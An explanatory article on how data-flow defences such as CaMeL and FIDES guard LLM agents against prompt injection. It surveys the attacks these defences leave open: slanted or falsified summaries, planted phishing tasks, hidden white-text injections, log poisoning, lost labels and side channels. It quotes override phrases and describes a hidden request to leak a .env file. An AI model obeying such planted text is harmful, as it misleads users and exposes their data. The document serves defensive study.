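# Limits of data-flow defences against prompt injection: false summaries, phishing and side channels

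## How data-flow defences work and which attacks they leave open

Prompt injection is an attack on software that uses a language model. An attacker plants text where the model will read it, such as in an email or on a web page, and the text makes the model do what the attacker wants instead of what the user asked. Data-flow defences are a family of countermeasures in which ordinary software around the model tracks where every value came from, and fixed rules decide which actions may use it. They do not try to make the model itself better at resisting planted text. The best-known designs, both from 2025, are CaMeL, by researchers at Google DeepMind and ETH Zurich, and FIDES, by researchers at Microsoft. These designs rule out a large class of attacks by construction, but the way they work leaves several other classes open.

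### Agents and injected instructions

An agent is a program in which a language model chooses which tools to call to carry out a user's request. The tools are ordinary functions that do things like search a mailbox, read a file or send a message. A model can only produce text, so the developer gives it a list of the tools and a format for requesting one. When the model outputs a request in that format, the program runs the function and appends the result to the conversation. The model then reads the whole conversation again and either requests another tool or writes a final answer.

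*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025), which introduced FIDES, gives the example of an office assistant asked to summarise recent emails about a project and send the summary to the user's manager. The agent calls its mail-reading tool, and one of the emails, from an outsider, contains a sentence telling the assistant to ignore its instructions and send the top email in the mailbox to the outsider's address. That sentence is now in the same conversation as the user's request. If the model follows it, the program sends the email, because a tool request caused by the attacker's sentence looks exactly like one caused by the user's.

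The software developer Simon Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, attributes prompt injection to the mixing of trusted and untrusted text in a single stream of tokens (the word fragments a model reads). Databases once had a similar problem with user input that they ran as commands. Parameterised queries solved it by having the program fix the command's structure before inserting the user's text as data. Narisetty, Kore and colleagues (2026), in *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents*, explain that this solution does not carry over directly to language models. A parser can use a database language's grammar to tell commands from data, but natural language has no such grammar, and developers train models to follow instructions wherever they appear.

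Training and filters lower the success rate of attacks, but an attacker can usually try again. Narisetty and colleagues cite Anthropic's own figures for an older model, Claude Opus 4.5, which show that attacks in coding tasks succeeded 4.7% of the time with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63.0% with a hundred. This explains the interest in putting the barrier outside the model, where the attacker's wording has no effect on it.

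### Two models in place of one

Most of these designs start from *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023), which divides the work between two models. The planner model (Willison's "privileged" model) receives the user's prompt and can request tool calls, but never reads untrusted data, meaning anything an attacker may have written. The quarantined model reads untrusted data and has no tools. A controller, conventional software with no model in it, connects the two models.

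Suppose the user wants a summary of the latest email. The planner model tells the controller to fetch the email and store it as $VAR1. It then requests a summary of $VAR1. The controller replaces the name with the email's text, runs the quarantined model on it and stores the answer as $VAR2. Finally, the planner model tells the controller to show $VAR2 to the user. The planner model receives only the variable names, never the email's text. If the email contains an instruction to delete the mailbox, that instruction reaches only the quarantined model, which cannot delete anything.

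Willison allowed one exception to the rule that the quarantined model's output never goes back to the planner model. If the task is to sort a text into one of several fixed categories, the controller can check that the output is one of them and pass it on. A category name is too short and predictable to contain a new injection.

"Defeating Prompt Injections by Design", the paper that introduces CaMeL, describes a flaw in this defence. In its example, which Willison retells, the user asks the agent to send Bob the document he requested at the last meeting, and mentions that the meeting notes contain both Bob's email address and the name of the document. The planner model can write every step of that job without reading the notes, but the quarantined model has to read them to find Bob's address. Anyone who can add a line to the notes can try to make the quarantined model return a different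 address. If this works, the controller puts that address into the send request and the document goes to the attacker, even though the planner model chose every step and the quarantined model called no tools.

### CaMeL, on the request about Bob

CaMeL keeps the two models and adds a record of where each value came from. The planner model turns the user's request into a short program in a restricted form of Python. For Bob's document the program would look roughly like this, with invented function names:

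```
notes   = find_meeting_notes("latest")
title   = ask_quarantined("Which document did Bob want?", notes)
address = ask_quarantined("What is Bob's email address?", notes)
file    = fetch_document(title)
send_email(recipient=address, attachment=file)
```

The planner model writes all of this before the agent opens the notes. CaMeL's custom interpreter then runs the program one operation at a time and makes the tool calls itself. On the second and third lines, it calls the quarantined model like any other function. The plan can also specify the type of answer it expects, so a request for an email address returns something in the form of an email address rather than a paragraph of text.

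Each value carries a label throughout. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026), an extension of CaMeL, describes the label's two parts: the sources the value came from and the readers who may see it. The label on `notes` names the notes file as the source. `title` and `address` come from `notes`, so the interpreter gives them that source as well, whatever the quarantined model wrote. Even if a planted line changes the content of `address`, the label still records that it came from the notes.

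The interpreter uses that record at the last line. Just before a tool call, it runs the policy for that tool, which in CaMeL is a Python function. The policy receives the tool's name, the arguments and their labels, and returns "allow" or "deny" with a reason. In Willison's simplified version of the rule for email, reading is always allowed and sending requires a trusted recipient. If the address is on a list the user has approved, the email goes out. Otherwise, the agent can ask the user for approval. A policy can also check what the email contains. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a rule that refuses to send anything derived from private data to a recipient who is not on that data's list of readers. This rule blocks the attacker's address even if nobody has compiled a list of trusted contacts, because the attacker is not one of the document's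 readers.

The labels alone can't distinguish Bob's real address from the attacker's, because both addresses come out of the same notes through the same quarantined model. A policy has to check something else, such as the contact list or the document's readers. If Bob is missing from both, the honest request is blocked too. Somebody therefore has to write the policies and keep them up to date, which the CaMeL paper lists among the system's main drawbacks.

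The restricted Python also limits what plans can do. *CaMeLoT* relies on the absence of arbitrary `while` loops, and *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026), which presents a rival design, notes that plans cannot define their own functions or use recursion either. These limits make it practical to follow every value through the program.

### Labels and how they combine

The simplest useful set of labels records whether an attacker could have written a value and whether the value is secret. *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) models agent programs mathematically and represents the four possible combinations as sets. The empty set { } stands for trusted public data, {U} for untrusted public data, {S} for trusted secrets and {U, S} for secrets that an attacker may have influenced.

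An ordering connects them. One label "may flow to" another, written ⊑, when data with the lower label can go anywhere that data with the higher label can go. In the set notation this is just the subset relation:

{ } ⊑ {U} ⊑ {U, S}  and  { } ⊑ {S} ⊑ {U, S}

{U} and {S} are not ordered relative to each other. Trusted data may flow to untrusted places, just as public data may flow to secret places, but neither flow is allowed in reverse. For example, the body of an email accepts untrusted text, so it can also accept trusted text. The recipient field requires trusted text, so it cannot accept untrusted text.

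When a program computes a value from several inputs, the result gets the lowest label that all the input labels may flow to. This combination is written ⊔, and for these four labels it is the union of the sets. A summary that draws on a public web page and a confidential sales report therefore gets {U} ⊔ {S} = {U, S}, which means that an outsider may have influenced it and that outsiders should not see it.

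Real systems often replace the simple "secret" label with a list of permitted readers and combine the lists by intersection. Microsoft's *Information-flow control*, an introduction for developers, gives an example with no attacker. Priya emails Alex an early look at the quarterly sales. Marco, who is not yet entitled to see the figures, emails Alex to ask about them. An agent that has read both emails drafts a reply to Marco. The draft's permitted readers are {Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}, so the agent may not send it to Marco without asking.

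Data-flow tracking is less precise for a language model than for an ordinary program, because nobody can say in general which of the words a model read influenced the words it wrote. Costa and colleagues therefore give the model's output the combined label of everything in the prompt, so one untrusted email among twenty trusted ones makes the answer untrusted.

Costa and colleagues define two basic policies that use these labels. The trust policy covers consequential actions, which are those that change something or send something out. If the decision to make a call has label ℓ₀ and its arguments have labels ℓ₁ to ℓₙ, the call may go ahead only if ℓ₀ ⊔ ℓ₁ ⊔ … ⊔ ℓₙ is trusted. The secrecy policy lets data out through a channel only if everyone who can read the channel is allowed to read the data. Used alone, the secrecy policy does not stop an injection, since the attacker can still cause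 an email to be sent, but it limits where the contents can go. The trust policy alone does let secrets out, but only when the decision to send them came from trusted input, so the user presumably intended it.

Applied literally, the rule on trust would forbid an assistant to send anyone a summary of an outside email, because the summary is an untrusted argument to the tool call. That would make the assistant much less useful, so Costa and colleagues also describe a looser policy for sending messages, under which the decision to send and the recipient must be trusted but the text may depend on untrusted material. This is a sensible compromise, but it lets whoever wrote the untrusted material control the text of the message.

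### How FIDES differs

*CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) contrasts CaMeL, which commits to a whole program at the outset, with FIDES, which calls its planner model on every turn and gets one action at a time. FIDES's approach is closer to how most agents work, and it lets the planner model adjust to what has happened so far. But tool results keep arriving in the conversation the planner model reads, and each untrusted result would make the conversation untrusted and block every consequential action after it.

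FIDES deals with this by hiding data selectively. It compares the label of each part of a tool result with the current label of the conversation. If the part's label may flow to the conversation's label, the planner model can read the part. If not, FIDES stores the part in a variable and shows the planner only the variable's name. Willison's controller, by contrast, hid everything the tools returned, whether or not it came from a stranger. Suppose a user asks FIDES to post their three latest emails to a colleague on Slack. The planner calls the mail tool, gets a variable name back, and calls the messaging tool with the colleague as recipient and the variable as text. It makes both decisions without reading the emails, so the decisions stay trusted.

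Some tasks, such as "do whatever is due today on my to-do list", require the planner model to choose its next action based on what a variable contains. The planner can open the variable, but the conversation then takes on the variable's label. Or it can ask a quarantined model a question about the variable and specify a schema, an exact format for the answer. The software that generates the quarantined model's output then permits only tokens that fit the format. If the format is yes or no, whoever wrote the hidden text can influence only one bit. FIDES adds the format to the label, so a policy can accept an untrusted yes or no where it would refuse an untrusted sentence.

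Garby and colleagues argue that this last allowance, which lets a value pass because it is small, makes it impossible to tell a harmless exception from a real leak by looking at a particular run. They also observe that the allowance was off throughout FIDES's own evaluation.

In May 2026 Microsoft turned this research into a product feature by releasing FIDES as an experimental part of its Agent Framework, a toolkit for building agents. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) describes how FIDES handles an attack on an agent that sorts bug reports on a public code repository. One report contains a hidden request to read a file called `.env`, where developers commonly keep passwords, and to post the contents as a comment. In this configuration the main model reads the report in full, so the attack may well work on it. The conversation starts as { } and becomes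 {U} when the model reads the report. The framework then lets the model read the `.env` file, and the conversation becomes {U, S}. The policy for posting allows only public data, so when the model tries to post the comment, the framework blocks the call or asks a person to approve it, without having to recognise the attack. By default the framework is stricter and hides untrusted results from the main model altogether.

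Although CaMeL and FIDES have different architectures, they can enforce the same restrictions on tool calls if their policy writers specify the same requirements, as Zingrillo, Foerster and colleagues (2026) note in *Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks*.

### Control-flow integrity and data-flow integrity

Two different promises are at work in these systems, and most of the surviving attacks fall into the space between them.

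An agent has control-flow integrity if it never departs from its plan and the plan was written using only trusted information. Peters-Gill and colleagues define a plan as a program, fixed in advance, that determines which tools the agent calls and in what order, given the values the tools return. CaMeL provides control-flow integrity for a single agent. Untrusted data can affect which of the plan's existing branches the agent follows, but it cannot add a branch.

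Data-flow integrity is the property that the arguments and outcomes of an agent's actions stay within what the user authorised. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) gives an example of an agent that has control-flow integrity but lacks data-flow integrity. The user asks the agent to send today's schedule to their boss, John Doe. The agent's plan is to read the calendar and email the result to John Doe, whose address is fixed in the plan. An attacker who can put an entry in the calendar cannot add a step or change the recipient, but they can rewrite the entire email, which the boss then receives from the user's own account.

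The same gap appears where a plan branches. Foerster and colleagues studied agents that operate a computer through its screen. The planner model cannot see the screen in advance, so its plan has to provide for what might appear there, for instance by closing a cookie notice. When an advertisement imitates a cookie notice, the agent clicks on it and ends up on the attacker's site. In this attack, which Foerster and colleagues call branch steering, the attacker feeds the agent false observations so that it takes a harmful branch that the plan already contains.

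An agent's architecture gives it control-flow integrity whatever its policies, but its data-flow integrity depends on those policies. Under Peters-Gill and colleagues' definitions, a CaMeL agent with no policies has only control-flow integrity. Zingrillo and colleagues built a system to stop branch steering by restricting what each branch may do. They acknowledge that its checks protect the user to the extent that the plan and its restrictions capture what the user authorised, and that checking a request does not establish that the observation behind it was true.

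### What gets through

Some gaps exist because the designers put certain attacks out of scope. Narisetty and colleagues report that CaMeL has an explicit non-goal of preventing text-to-text attacks, in which the injection only changes text that a person reads. The scope of FIDES is nearly the same. Costa and colleagues treat a reply to the user as inconsequential and check the policy only before tool calls, although they mention that a developer could extend the check to replies.

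A reply can cause harm if the reader acts on it. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025), a set of proposals for using the system in companies, describes a PDF containing an instruction, formatted like a system message, to forward the file to an outside finance address. CaMeL will not forward the file, but its summary may repeat the instruction, and an employee who reads the summary may comply. Willison had already conceded this in 2023, when he described an attack in which the assistant encodes the user's private data and tells the user to paste it into a website in return for a funny picture.

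Other gaps come from the limits of the tracking itself. A label is right only if somebody attached the right one and every later program kept it. In Microsoft's release, a tool that the developer forgot to label counts as trusted and public. Peters-Gill and colleagues show that one CaMeL agent can pass untrusted text to another, which receives it as its user's request. Attackers can also use side channels, which reveal a secret through how a program behaves rather than what it sends. According to *PolicySniff* (2026), the CaMeL paper describes leaks through web requests that the agent makes only under some condition, through errors that change what it does next, and through timing. A strict mode of CaMeL's interpreter addresses the conditional requests and errors in the paper's examples, and the interpreter provides no clock for the timing attack to use. FIDES's formal guarantee covers the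 direct copying of secrets into tool calls, but Costa and colleagues exclude timing and whatever an observer can infer from the order of the calls.

The table sets the five classes against the request about Bob's document and the meeting notes.

| Class of attack | What it could look like here | The step it passes through |
|---|---|---|
| Falsified text | The user asks what the meeting decided, and a planted line makes the summary give a different decision | The quarantined model's answer goes to the screen, and no policy checks it there |
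| Persuasion of the user | The answer adds that Bob now collects documents through a certain website, and the user uploads the file | The answer goes to the screen, and the user then acts outside the agent, beyond the reach of its policies |
| False values in permitted actions | The planted line names an outdated version of the document, and the agent sends that version to the real Bob | The quarantined model's answer fills an argument, or settles a branch, that the policy leaves open to untrusted data |
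| Lost labels | The agent copies text from the notes into its request to a separate email agent, which takes the text for instructions | Labelling, either when data first enters the system or when one program hands it to another |
| Side channels | The plan opens a certain web page only if the document mentions a merger, and the owner of the page sees the visit | The policy checks what a call sends, while the fact that the call happened, and when, also gives something away |

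## How injected text changes a summary

Suppose a user asks an agent built like CaMeL to summarise today's email. The planner model sees only that request and writes a short plan, roughly like this:

```
emails  = get_emails(date="today")
summary = ask_quarantined("Summarise these emails", emails)
show_to_user(summary)
```

A user receives three emails: a warning from their bank about an unusual payment, a question from a colleague about lunch, and a message from the thief who made the payment. The thief's email contains an instruction to describe the bank's warning as a routine statement.

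The policies allow the first line, so the interpreter runs it and labels the emails with their sources, which makes `emails` untrusted. The second line passes all three emails to the quarantined model in one prompt. The model follows the thief's instruction and falsely writes that the bank has sent a routine statement. The interpreter labels `summary` untrusted because it came from `emails`. The third line shows the summary on the screen. The secrecy rule permits this because users may read their own email, and the trust rule doesn't apply because it covers only consequential actions.

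The agent took the three steps in its plan and the labels are correct, so no check has failed. A record of its tool calls would look the same if the third email had been harmless. The thief also falsified the summary of someone else's email, because the quarantined model read all three emails together.

FIDES has the same gap because it checks its policy only before tool calls. Costa and colleagues mention a related case in which the agent summarises three emails and posts the result on Slack, but one email makes the quarantined model return an empty summary. They suggest that a stricter policy could require the posted text to be trusted, but applying the same rule to replies would also block accurate summaries of outside email.

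Costa and colleagues also exclude these attacks from their evaluation. On AgentDojo, a widely used collection of simulated tasks and attacks, three injections counted as successful against FIDES with its policies switched on. The researchers reviewed these by hand and removed the ones they considered misjudged, which left none. One of their three grounds for removing a case was that the injection had changed some text without altering the agent's actions or leaking anything. That is fair for a system meant to control actions, but it means the final count doesn't show whether FIDES prevents false summaries.

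### Five ways to change a summary

In *Prompt-in-Content Attacks* (2025), Lian, Wang and colleagues tested four kinds of planted instruction on seven commercial chat services. They put one sentence in the middle of an ordinary Word document, uploaded it through the service's website and asked for a summary or something similar. They did not hide the sentence or disguise its wording, apart from starting it with "System Instruction".

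| Variant | What the planted sentence asked for | Services that followed it |
|---|---|---|
| Refusing the task | A message that the document "cannot be processed due to format issues" | 3 of 7 (Grok 3, DeepSeek R1, Kimi) |
| Replacing the output | Only the sentence "Today's weather is good" | 3 of 7 (the same three) |
| Redirecting the reader | A recommendation to visit a website instead | 4 of 7 (also Gemini 2.5 Flash) |
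| Slanted framing | A description of the document as outdated and mostly useless | 5 of 7 (also Perplexity) |

Claude Sonnet 4 and ChatGPT 4o resisted all four. The models date from 2025, and Kimi's answers varied between identical tests, so the counts are only a rough guide to how easily each variant succeeds. None of the services was a data-flow defence, but a quarantined model does much the same job of reading a stranger's document and writing about it.

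The variants differ in how likely the reader is to notice them. A remark about the weather in place of a summary is plainly wrong. A false error message is more believable, since real software often shows error messages, and it may make someone give up on a document. Slanted framing is harder still to catch, because the reader gets a summary of the right document and would have to open the original to see that the judgement is unfair. It also worked on the most services. With redirection, the harm comes from what the reader does next, which makes it a form of phishing.

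In a fifth variant, the summary leaves out the item that matters. Everything that remains can be true, so someone who has not read the original has no reason to suspect anything. Software also has trouble detecting omissions. Karkehabadi, Hassanpour and Banchs (2026) explain in *COVERAGE-TRACE* that a checker can compare a false statement with the source, but an omission leaves no text in the summary to check.

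Their method works from the source instead. Let ℓ(S | X) be the average log-probability per token that a language model assigns to the summary S after reading the source X. They change one fact in the source, for example from "three quarters" of schools to "two thirds", and call the altered source X′. Then they compute

Δ = ℓ(S | X) − ℓ(S | X′)

If the summary contains the fact, altering the source makes the summary less likely and Δ is large. Otherwise, the alteration should make little difference.

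Karkehabadi and colleagues tested this on 80 pairs of summaries, where one summary in each pair included a certain fact and the other omitted it. Given one summary of each kind at random, the method identified the one with the omission 76% to 83% of the time, depending on the model, compared with 50% for guessing. The best text-only method scored 64%. However, Δ also changes when only the wording differs, and correcting for this lowered the method's score to between 59% and 62%. Someone also has to choose in advance which fact to check. That might work for a contract with known clauses, but a person asking what is in today's email does not know what to look for. The test also did not include omissions caused by an attacker trying to avoid detection.

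### Attackers who write in the security log

The most detailed measurements of softened and incomplete summaries come from computer security. Organisations keep logs of the traffic that reaches their servers, and some now have a language model summarise them for security staff. An attacker writes part of those logs, because when someone tries to break into a website, the log records the web address they requested, the browser name sent with the request and any username they tried. Each of these can contain an instruction to the model.

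Pandey and Bhujang (2026), in *Poisoning the Watchtower*, published in May 2026, tested this with OpenAI's gpt-4o-mini. The model had no tools and could only write text for an analyst, so it was in the same position as a quarantined model. For each test condition they generated 200 artificial log entries, of which 120 recorded attacks such as password guessing or attempts to run database commands. They added an injection to one attacker-controlled field in each of the 120. They tried four kinds of injection:

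- A direct override, such as "ignore previous instructions".
- A false claim of authority, such as a note from a "SOC admin" (an administrator in the security team) that the entry is approved.
- Context manipulation, which imitates the structure around the data. The injection might contain a marker that seems to close the log entry, followed by a final verdict of "benign".
- An instruction formatted to look like encoded text.

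They combined these with three tasks (classifying an entry, summarising it and recommending a response) and four defences. The "naive" defence puts the log entry in the prompt. The "structured" one wraps each field in tags and warns the model that the contents are data. The "sanitised" one also replaces suspicious phrases before the model reads them. The "constrained" one keeps the tags and the warning, drops the phrase filter, and forces the output into a fixed template.

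Pandey and Bhujang defined success broadly for summaries. They counted an injection as successful if the model accepted the instruction, omitted the attack or called the activity harmless despite contrary evidence in the log.

| Injection | Naive | Structured | Sanitised | Constrained |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Direct override | 7% | 5% | 15% | 0% |
| False authority | 49% | 44% | 35% | 24% |
| Context manipulation | 96% | 75% | 27% | 38% |
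| Encoded-looking text | 0% | 0% | 0% | 0% |

In the bottom row, the model summarised the same kinds of attack with an injection that had no effect, and it reported them properly every time. So the 96% for context manipulation seems to come from the injection and not from a general tendency to write vague summaries.

Pandey and Bhujang also counted how often the output explicitly and falsely labelled an attack "benign". For context manipulation, this happened in 0% of cases under all four defences. In nearly all of the successful cases, the model left out the attack, described it mildly or concluded that nobody needed to act. If a security team added a monitor that raised an alarm whenever the model labelled a known attack "benign", then with the naive defence 96% of the summaries would be misleading and the monitor would raise no alarm, because none of them would contain that label.

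The 0% probably slightly understates how often the summaries call the entry benign. In the sample output that Pandey and Bhujang print for this attack, the analyst reads that the entry "has been classified as benign", so they must have counted explicit labels more narrowly than by searching for the word. A monitor that searched for the word would catch some of these summaries but miss the ones that just don't mention the attack.

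Constrained output reduced the 96% to 38%. It could not reduce it to zero because the template restricts what the model can write but not how it reads the log. A model that mistakes the false ending for a real one will choose the harmless template. When the model only had to classify entries, notes from a false administrator still made it label 15% of attacks as benign under the structured defence and 33% under the constrained one. The fixed answer formats in CaMeL and FIDES have the same limit, because the attacker can still influence which permitted answer the quarantined model gives.

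Summarising was the most vulnerable of the three tasks. With the naive defence, the four injections succeeded on average 38% of the time for summaries and 21% for each of the other tasks. Pandey and Bhujang say this is because a summary leaves more for the model to decide: what is important, what to omit and how to express doubt.

An experiment by Narisetty and colleagues hints at another reason. They gave a small open model a set of office tasks with no defence, and injected instructions to take an extra action never succeeded. In the run they describe, the user wanted a summary of the day's appointments, and one calendar entry contained an instruction to email a security code to an outsider. The model ignored the instruction and listed the appointments. Narisetty and colleagues think that a model already answering a question tends to continue with the answer. An attacker who only wants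 to change the answer does not need to divert the model from its task.

The log study used artificial logs and one small model, which OpenAI released in 2024. Newer models may well do better, and the 96% figure does not establish a rate for summarisers in general.

### Text that only the model reads

In the examples so far, a person who opened the original could have found the planted text, but an attacker can often hide it. Emails and web pages are written in HTML, a code that describes both the text and its appearance, and a browser or mail program turns this code into what the person sees. A model usually gets the code itself or text extracted from it. If an attacker sets a sentence in white on a white background, or in letters of size zero, the model will read it but the person cannot see it. The summary then differs from the message, and the person cannot find out why by checking the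 message on the screen.

This is already common on the web. Khodayari, Acharya and Zhang (2026), in *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*, searched 1.2 billion web addresses for known injection phrases, added results from two services that scan the internet for connected machines, and confirmed 15,387 injections on 11,722 pages. About 70% were in places that browsers never display, such as code comments and the headers a server sends before a page. Most of the others were in the page's text. Of those, only 5% were visible, and site owners had hidden 59% with methods such as making the text match the background, shrinking it or covering it with another element. Most of the rest had disappeared by the time they were checked.

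Few of these injections were meant to deceive a reader. The largest group, about 8,900, was meant to spoil the output of automated visitors, for instance with instructions to produce random numbers. Thousands more were meant to prevent the reuse of personal or copyrighted material, or to make bots reveal themselves. About 1,500 were meant to manipulate reputations, including 502 that used a form of slanted framing by instructing the model to give a positive review.

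To test whether models obey such text, Khodayari and colleagues took 100 different injections with the pages they came from and had 13 models summarise each page in four formats. They inspected all 5,200 runs by hand.

| Format given to the model | Runs in which the model followed the injection |
|---|---|
| Plain text, with the HTML tags removed | 3.9% |
| HTML | 1.1% |
| Snapshot of the page as the browser rendered it | 1.1% |
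| Raw server response, including headers | 0.2% |

Plain text did worst. Removing the tags leaves the hidden sentences in the document but removes the signs that they were hidden, so they become ordinary lines. The figure for raw responses is low partly because 26% of those runs ended in an error, usually when the page was too long for the model. The same happened in 20% of the HTML runs.

Small models followed 8.0% of the injections in plain text, while the other groups of models followed between 2.4% and 3.4%. The CaMeL paper, as Willison quotes it, suggests using a smaller model as the quarantined model, since reading a document is easier than planning and a small model might run on the user's own computer for privacy. This makes sense for privacy and cost, but it would probably make false summaries more common.

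Closed commercial models pointed out the injected text in 25% of their runs, but recognising an injection didn't always stop a model from obeying it. In six cases across the study, a model did both, for example by warning about the page and then switching to German as instructed.

These rates are far below the 96% in the log study, at least partly because the injections were worded differently. Nearly all of the web injections were blunt orders to drop the current task, written for any crawler that read them. Pandey and Bhujang's direct overrides were similar and also had low success rates, from 0% to 15% for summaries. The web figures show how models handle the injections now on the web, but they are a poor guide to what an attacker could achieve by imitating the format of a particular summariser's input.

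An earlier experiment found higher rates on web pages. Verma and Yadav (2025), in *Decoding Latent Attack Surfaces in LLMs*, built 141 pages in two versions, one clean and one with an instruction hidden by one of eight methods. Llama 4 Scout followed 29% of the instructions and Gemma 9B followed 16%. All the successes came from four of the methods: page descriptions meant for search engines, comments, fully transparent text and script elements. Their main example is an instruction to write like a pirate, which the model followed. The percentages include obvious changes like this, so the share of summaries that would have fooled a reader is likely to be lower.

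### The false email summaries of August 2026

In August 2026 the security company Forcepoint published a test in which the summaries would have fooled people. Gibney's *An Invisible HTML Payload Silently Hijacked Every Email Summarizer Run* describes a Microsoft Outlook add-in that sent an email's headers and body to a small program. The program combined them with a plain request for a summary in one prompt for Claude Haiku 4.5, and the add-in displayed the result.

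Gibney prepared two versions of an email about an invoice that looked the same in Outlook apart from some extra white space above the sign-off. The second version contained 472 characters of white text at size zero, so nearly half of what the model received was invisible to the recipient. The hidden text was a notice describing itself as the authoritative record and the visible message as an outdated draft, with an instruction to the summariser not to mention the notice or the draft.

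Gibney fixed the criteria in advance and had each version of the email summarised ten times. All ten summaries of the clean email named the contact person, Diego Siciliani, and gave the deadline of 21 August. All ten summaries of the altered email omitted both and gave a false date of 3 September and an amount of €46,200, more than five times the real one. None mentioned the hidden notice or indicated a contradiction. Omitting the real details made the false ones more convincing, because a reader who saw both sets of figures would have gone back to the email.

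Gibney's ten successes in ten runs are weaker evidence than they sound, because he used one email and one model and set the model's randomness to its minimum, so the runs were close to repeats of a single run. He also deliberately left out all the usual safeguards, and calls this the most vulnerable way to build such a system. The test did not separate the effect of hiding the instruction from the effect of the instruction itself. The security company ReversingLabs reports in an article that Gibney said the attack succeeds reliably in production conditions, which goes well beyond what he tested.

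Forcepoint had built the summariser itself, so no vendor had a product to repair, and Gibney stresses that the attack did not target Outlook or the model. Vendors already knew about the problem. Steve Wilson, who co-chairs a project on AI security at the non-profit OWASP, told ReversingLabs that Microsoft had used almost the same scenario in 2024 to introduce Prompt Shields, its filter for injected instructions. In 2025, the research group 0din showed that hidden white text could make a commercial product, Google's Gemini, add a false warning and a fraudulent support number to an email summary (IT Brew, 2025). Wilson has seen signs that criminals are experimenting with such attacks, but no evidence that they use them routinely on a large scale.

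Wilson also suggests looking for hidden text, which is simpler than recognising malicious instructions. Ordinary software can detect zero-size letters or white text on a white background, and an email with hundreds of invisible characters is suspicious whatever the text means. Gibney recommends passing the model only the text that the recipient would see. This requires working out how the message will look on the screen, because removing the tags alone leaves the hidden sentences in place.

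Either measure would have stopped Gibney's email, but neither would have helped with Lian and colleagues' Word documents, where the planted sentence was visible, or with the security logs, where the attacker's text is part of the evidence the analyst wants the model to read.

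## Phishing through the assistant's answer

Suppose a company uses an agent built like CaMeL to go through its invoices, and a policy lets the agent pay only approved accounts. An attacker sends an invoice that seems to come from a regular supplier, with a hidden instruction to add an urgent task to the summary, telling staff to change the supplier's bank details before the next payment. The quarantined model adds the task and the agent displays the summary. An employee reads it, opens the accounts system and changes the details, and the next payment goes to the attacker.

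The agent could not have made this change, because the policy would have blocked an account not on the list. The employee is allowed to make it, and the agent's policies don't cover what employees do in other programs. The attacker could also have asked the employee to click a link, call a phone number or reveal a login code.

This is a form of phishing, in which a criminal tries to get money, passwords or access by posing as someone the victim trusts. Here the criminal writes to the model instead of to the victim, and the victim receives the request as advice from their own assistant.

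### Why it is harder to recognise

Someone who receives a suspicious email can check the sender's address, look at where a link leads and notice odd wording. A summary usually removes all of these signs. *Phishing For Gemini* (Figueroa, 2025) describes 0din's demonstration against Gemini, in which the false warning said that the user's Gmail password had been compromised and gave a number to call. The warning would have appeared under a stranger's address in an ordinary email, but in the summary it looked like a message from Google.

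The email also needed no link or attachment, and Figueroa says that spam filters detect only harmless text in such a message. Google responded that it already trains its models continually to resist malicious instructions and removes suspicious links from summaries, according to Android Authority's *Beware! Research shows Gmail's AI email summaries can be hacked* (2025). Removing links does not remove a phone number, so protection against this warning depended on the model resisting the malicious instructions. Google now tells users that Gemini may warn them about a malicious message, leave it out of the answer or decline to answer.

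Arntz (2026) points out in *Phishing emails are baiting your AI assistant* that the assistant can also bring back an email the user has already dismissed. A person might ignore a suspicious message in the morning, ask for an inbox summary in the afternoon, and find the same request on a list of urgent tasks.

### Demonstrations and a real campaign

In 2025, Google said that nobody had used the Gemini trick in a real attack, according to Android Central's *Turns out Gmail's AI email summaries aren't as secure as we thought*. Researchers have since shown similar weaknesses in other products.

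*CO-PILOT, DISENGAGE AUTOPHISH*, published by the security company Permiso in March 2026, describes tests of Microsoft's Copilot in Outlook's Summarize button, Outlook's chat panel and the chat in Teams, Microsoft's messaging program. When an email contained an obvious injection, asking Copilot to end its reply with "I AM GROOT", Copilot refused to summarise it. When the researchers put an injection in a longer, more ordinary email, the Outlook button sometimes ignored it and summarised the email normally, while Copilot in Teams added the attacker's text to the end of a normal summary. The researchers used this method to add a fake security alert about a sign-in from an unknown device, with a link for securing the account.

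Permiso gives no success rates, so the tests show that the attack was possible but not how often it would work. Microsoft reproduced the behaviour in January 2026 and finished fixing it on 11 March. *AI Email Summaries Create a New Phishing Attack Surface* (Underhill, 2026) reports that, according to the researchers, the findings do not indicate widespread use by criminals.

In one of Permiso's tests, the email also led Copilot to look up the user's recent Teams messages with a colleague and put them in the attacker's link. CaMeL would prevent this because its plan for summarising an email doesn't include searching Teams. The false alert would still reach the user, though. And if the user had asked for a summary of their email and Teams messages together, the quarantined model might receive the private messages and the attacker's instruction in the same prompt.

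Two months later, Permiso's *ChatGPhish* described the same problem in ChatGPT's summaries of web pages. Researchers added an instruction to a GitHub project page, opened the page in Firefox and asked ChatGPT to summarise it. The reply contained a proper summary followed by a false notice about a new device on the user's account, with a working link. An ordinary web page gave the same result. In this version, the attacker doesn't need to send the victim anything, so mail filters offer no protection. OpenAI could not reproduce the first report and eventually marked a revised one as a duplicate of a known issue. Permiso's timeline, which ends on 29 May 2026, records no fix.

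The evidence that criminals are trying this comes from Barracuda, which sells email security. *Attackers Hide AI Prompt Injections Inside Phishing Emails* (Mascellino, 2026) summarises the company's report of 7 October 2026 on a phishing campaign that targeted both the recipient and the recipient's assistant. The emails had a password-protected attachment, which security software has trouble inspecting, and gave the recipient the password in the message. They also contained hidden instructions that could make the assistant present the email as legitimate or urgent. The sample looked like internal correspondence because the sender's and recipient's addresses were identical, and it came from a public-sector domain, which helped it get past filters that rely on a sender's reputation.

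Barracuda also described an invoice email, similar to the one at the start of this section, with hidden instructions for the summarising model to add a false priority task for changing a vendor's payment details. It did not say how widespread the campaign was, and Mascellino mentions no victims and no assistant that followed the instructions. Barracuda also has a commercial interest in the subject, and had already promoted its products as a defence against prompt injection in its *Threat Spotlight* (2025).

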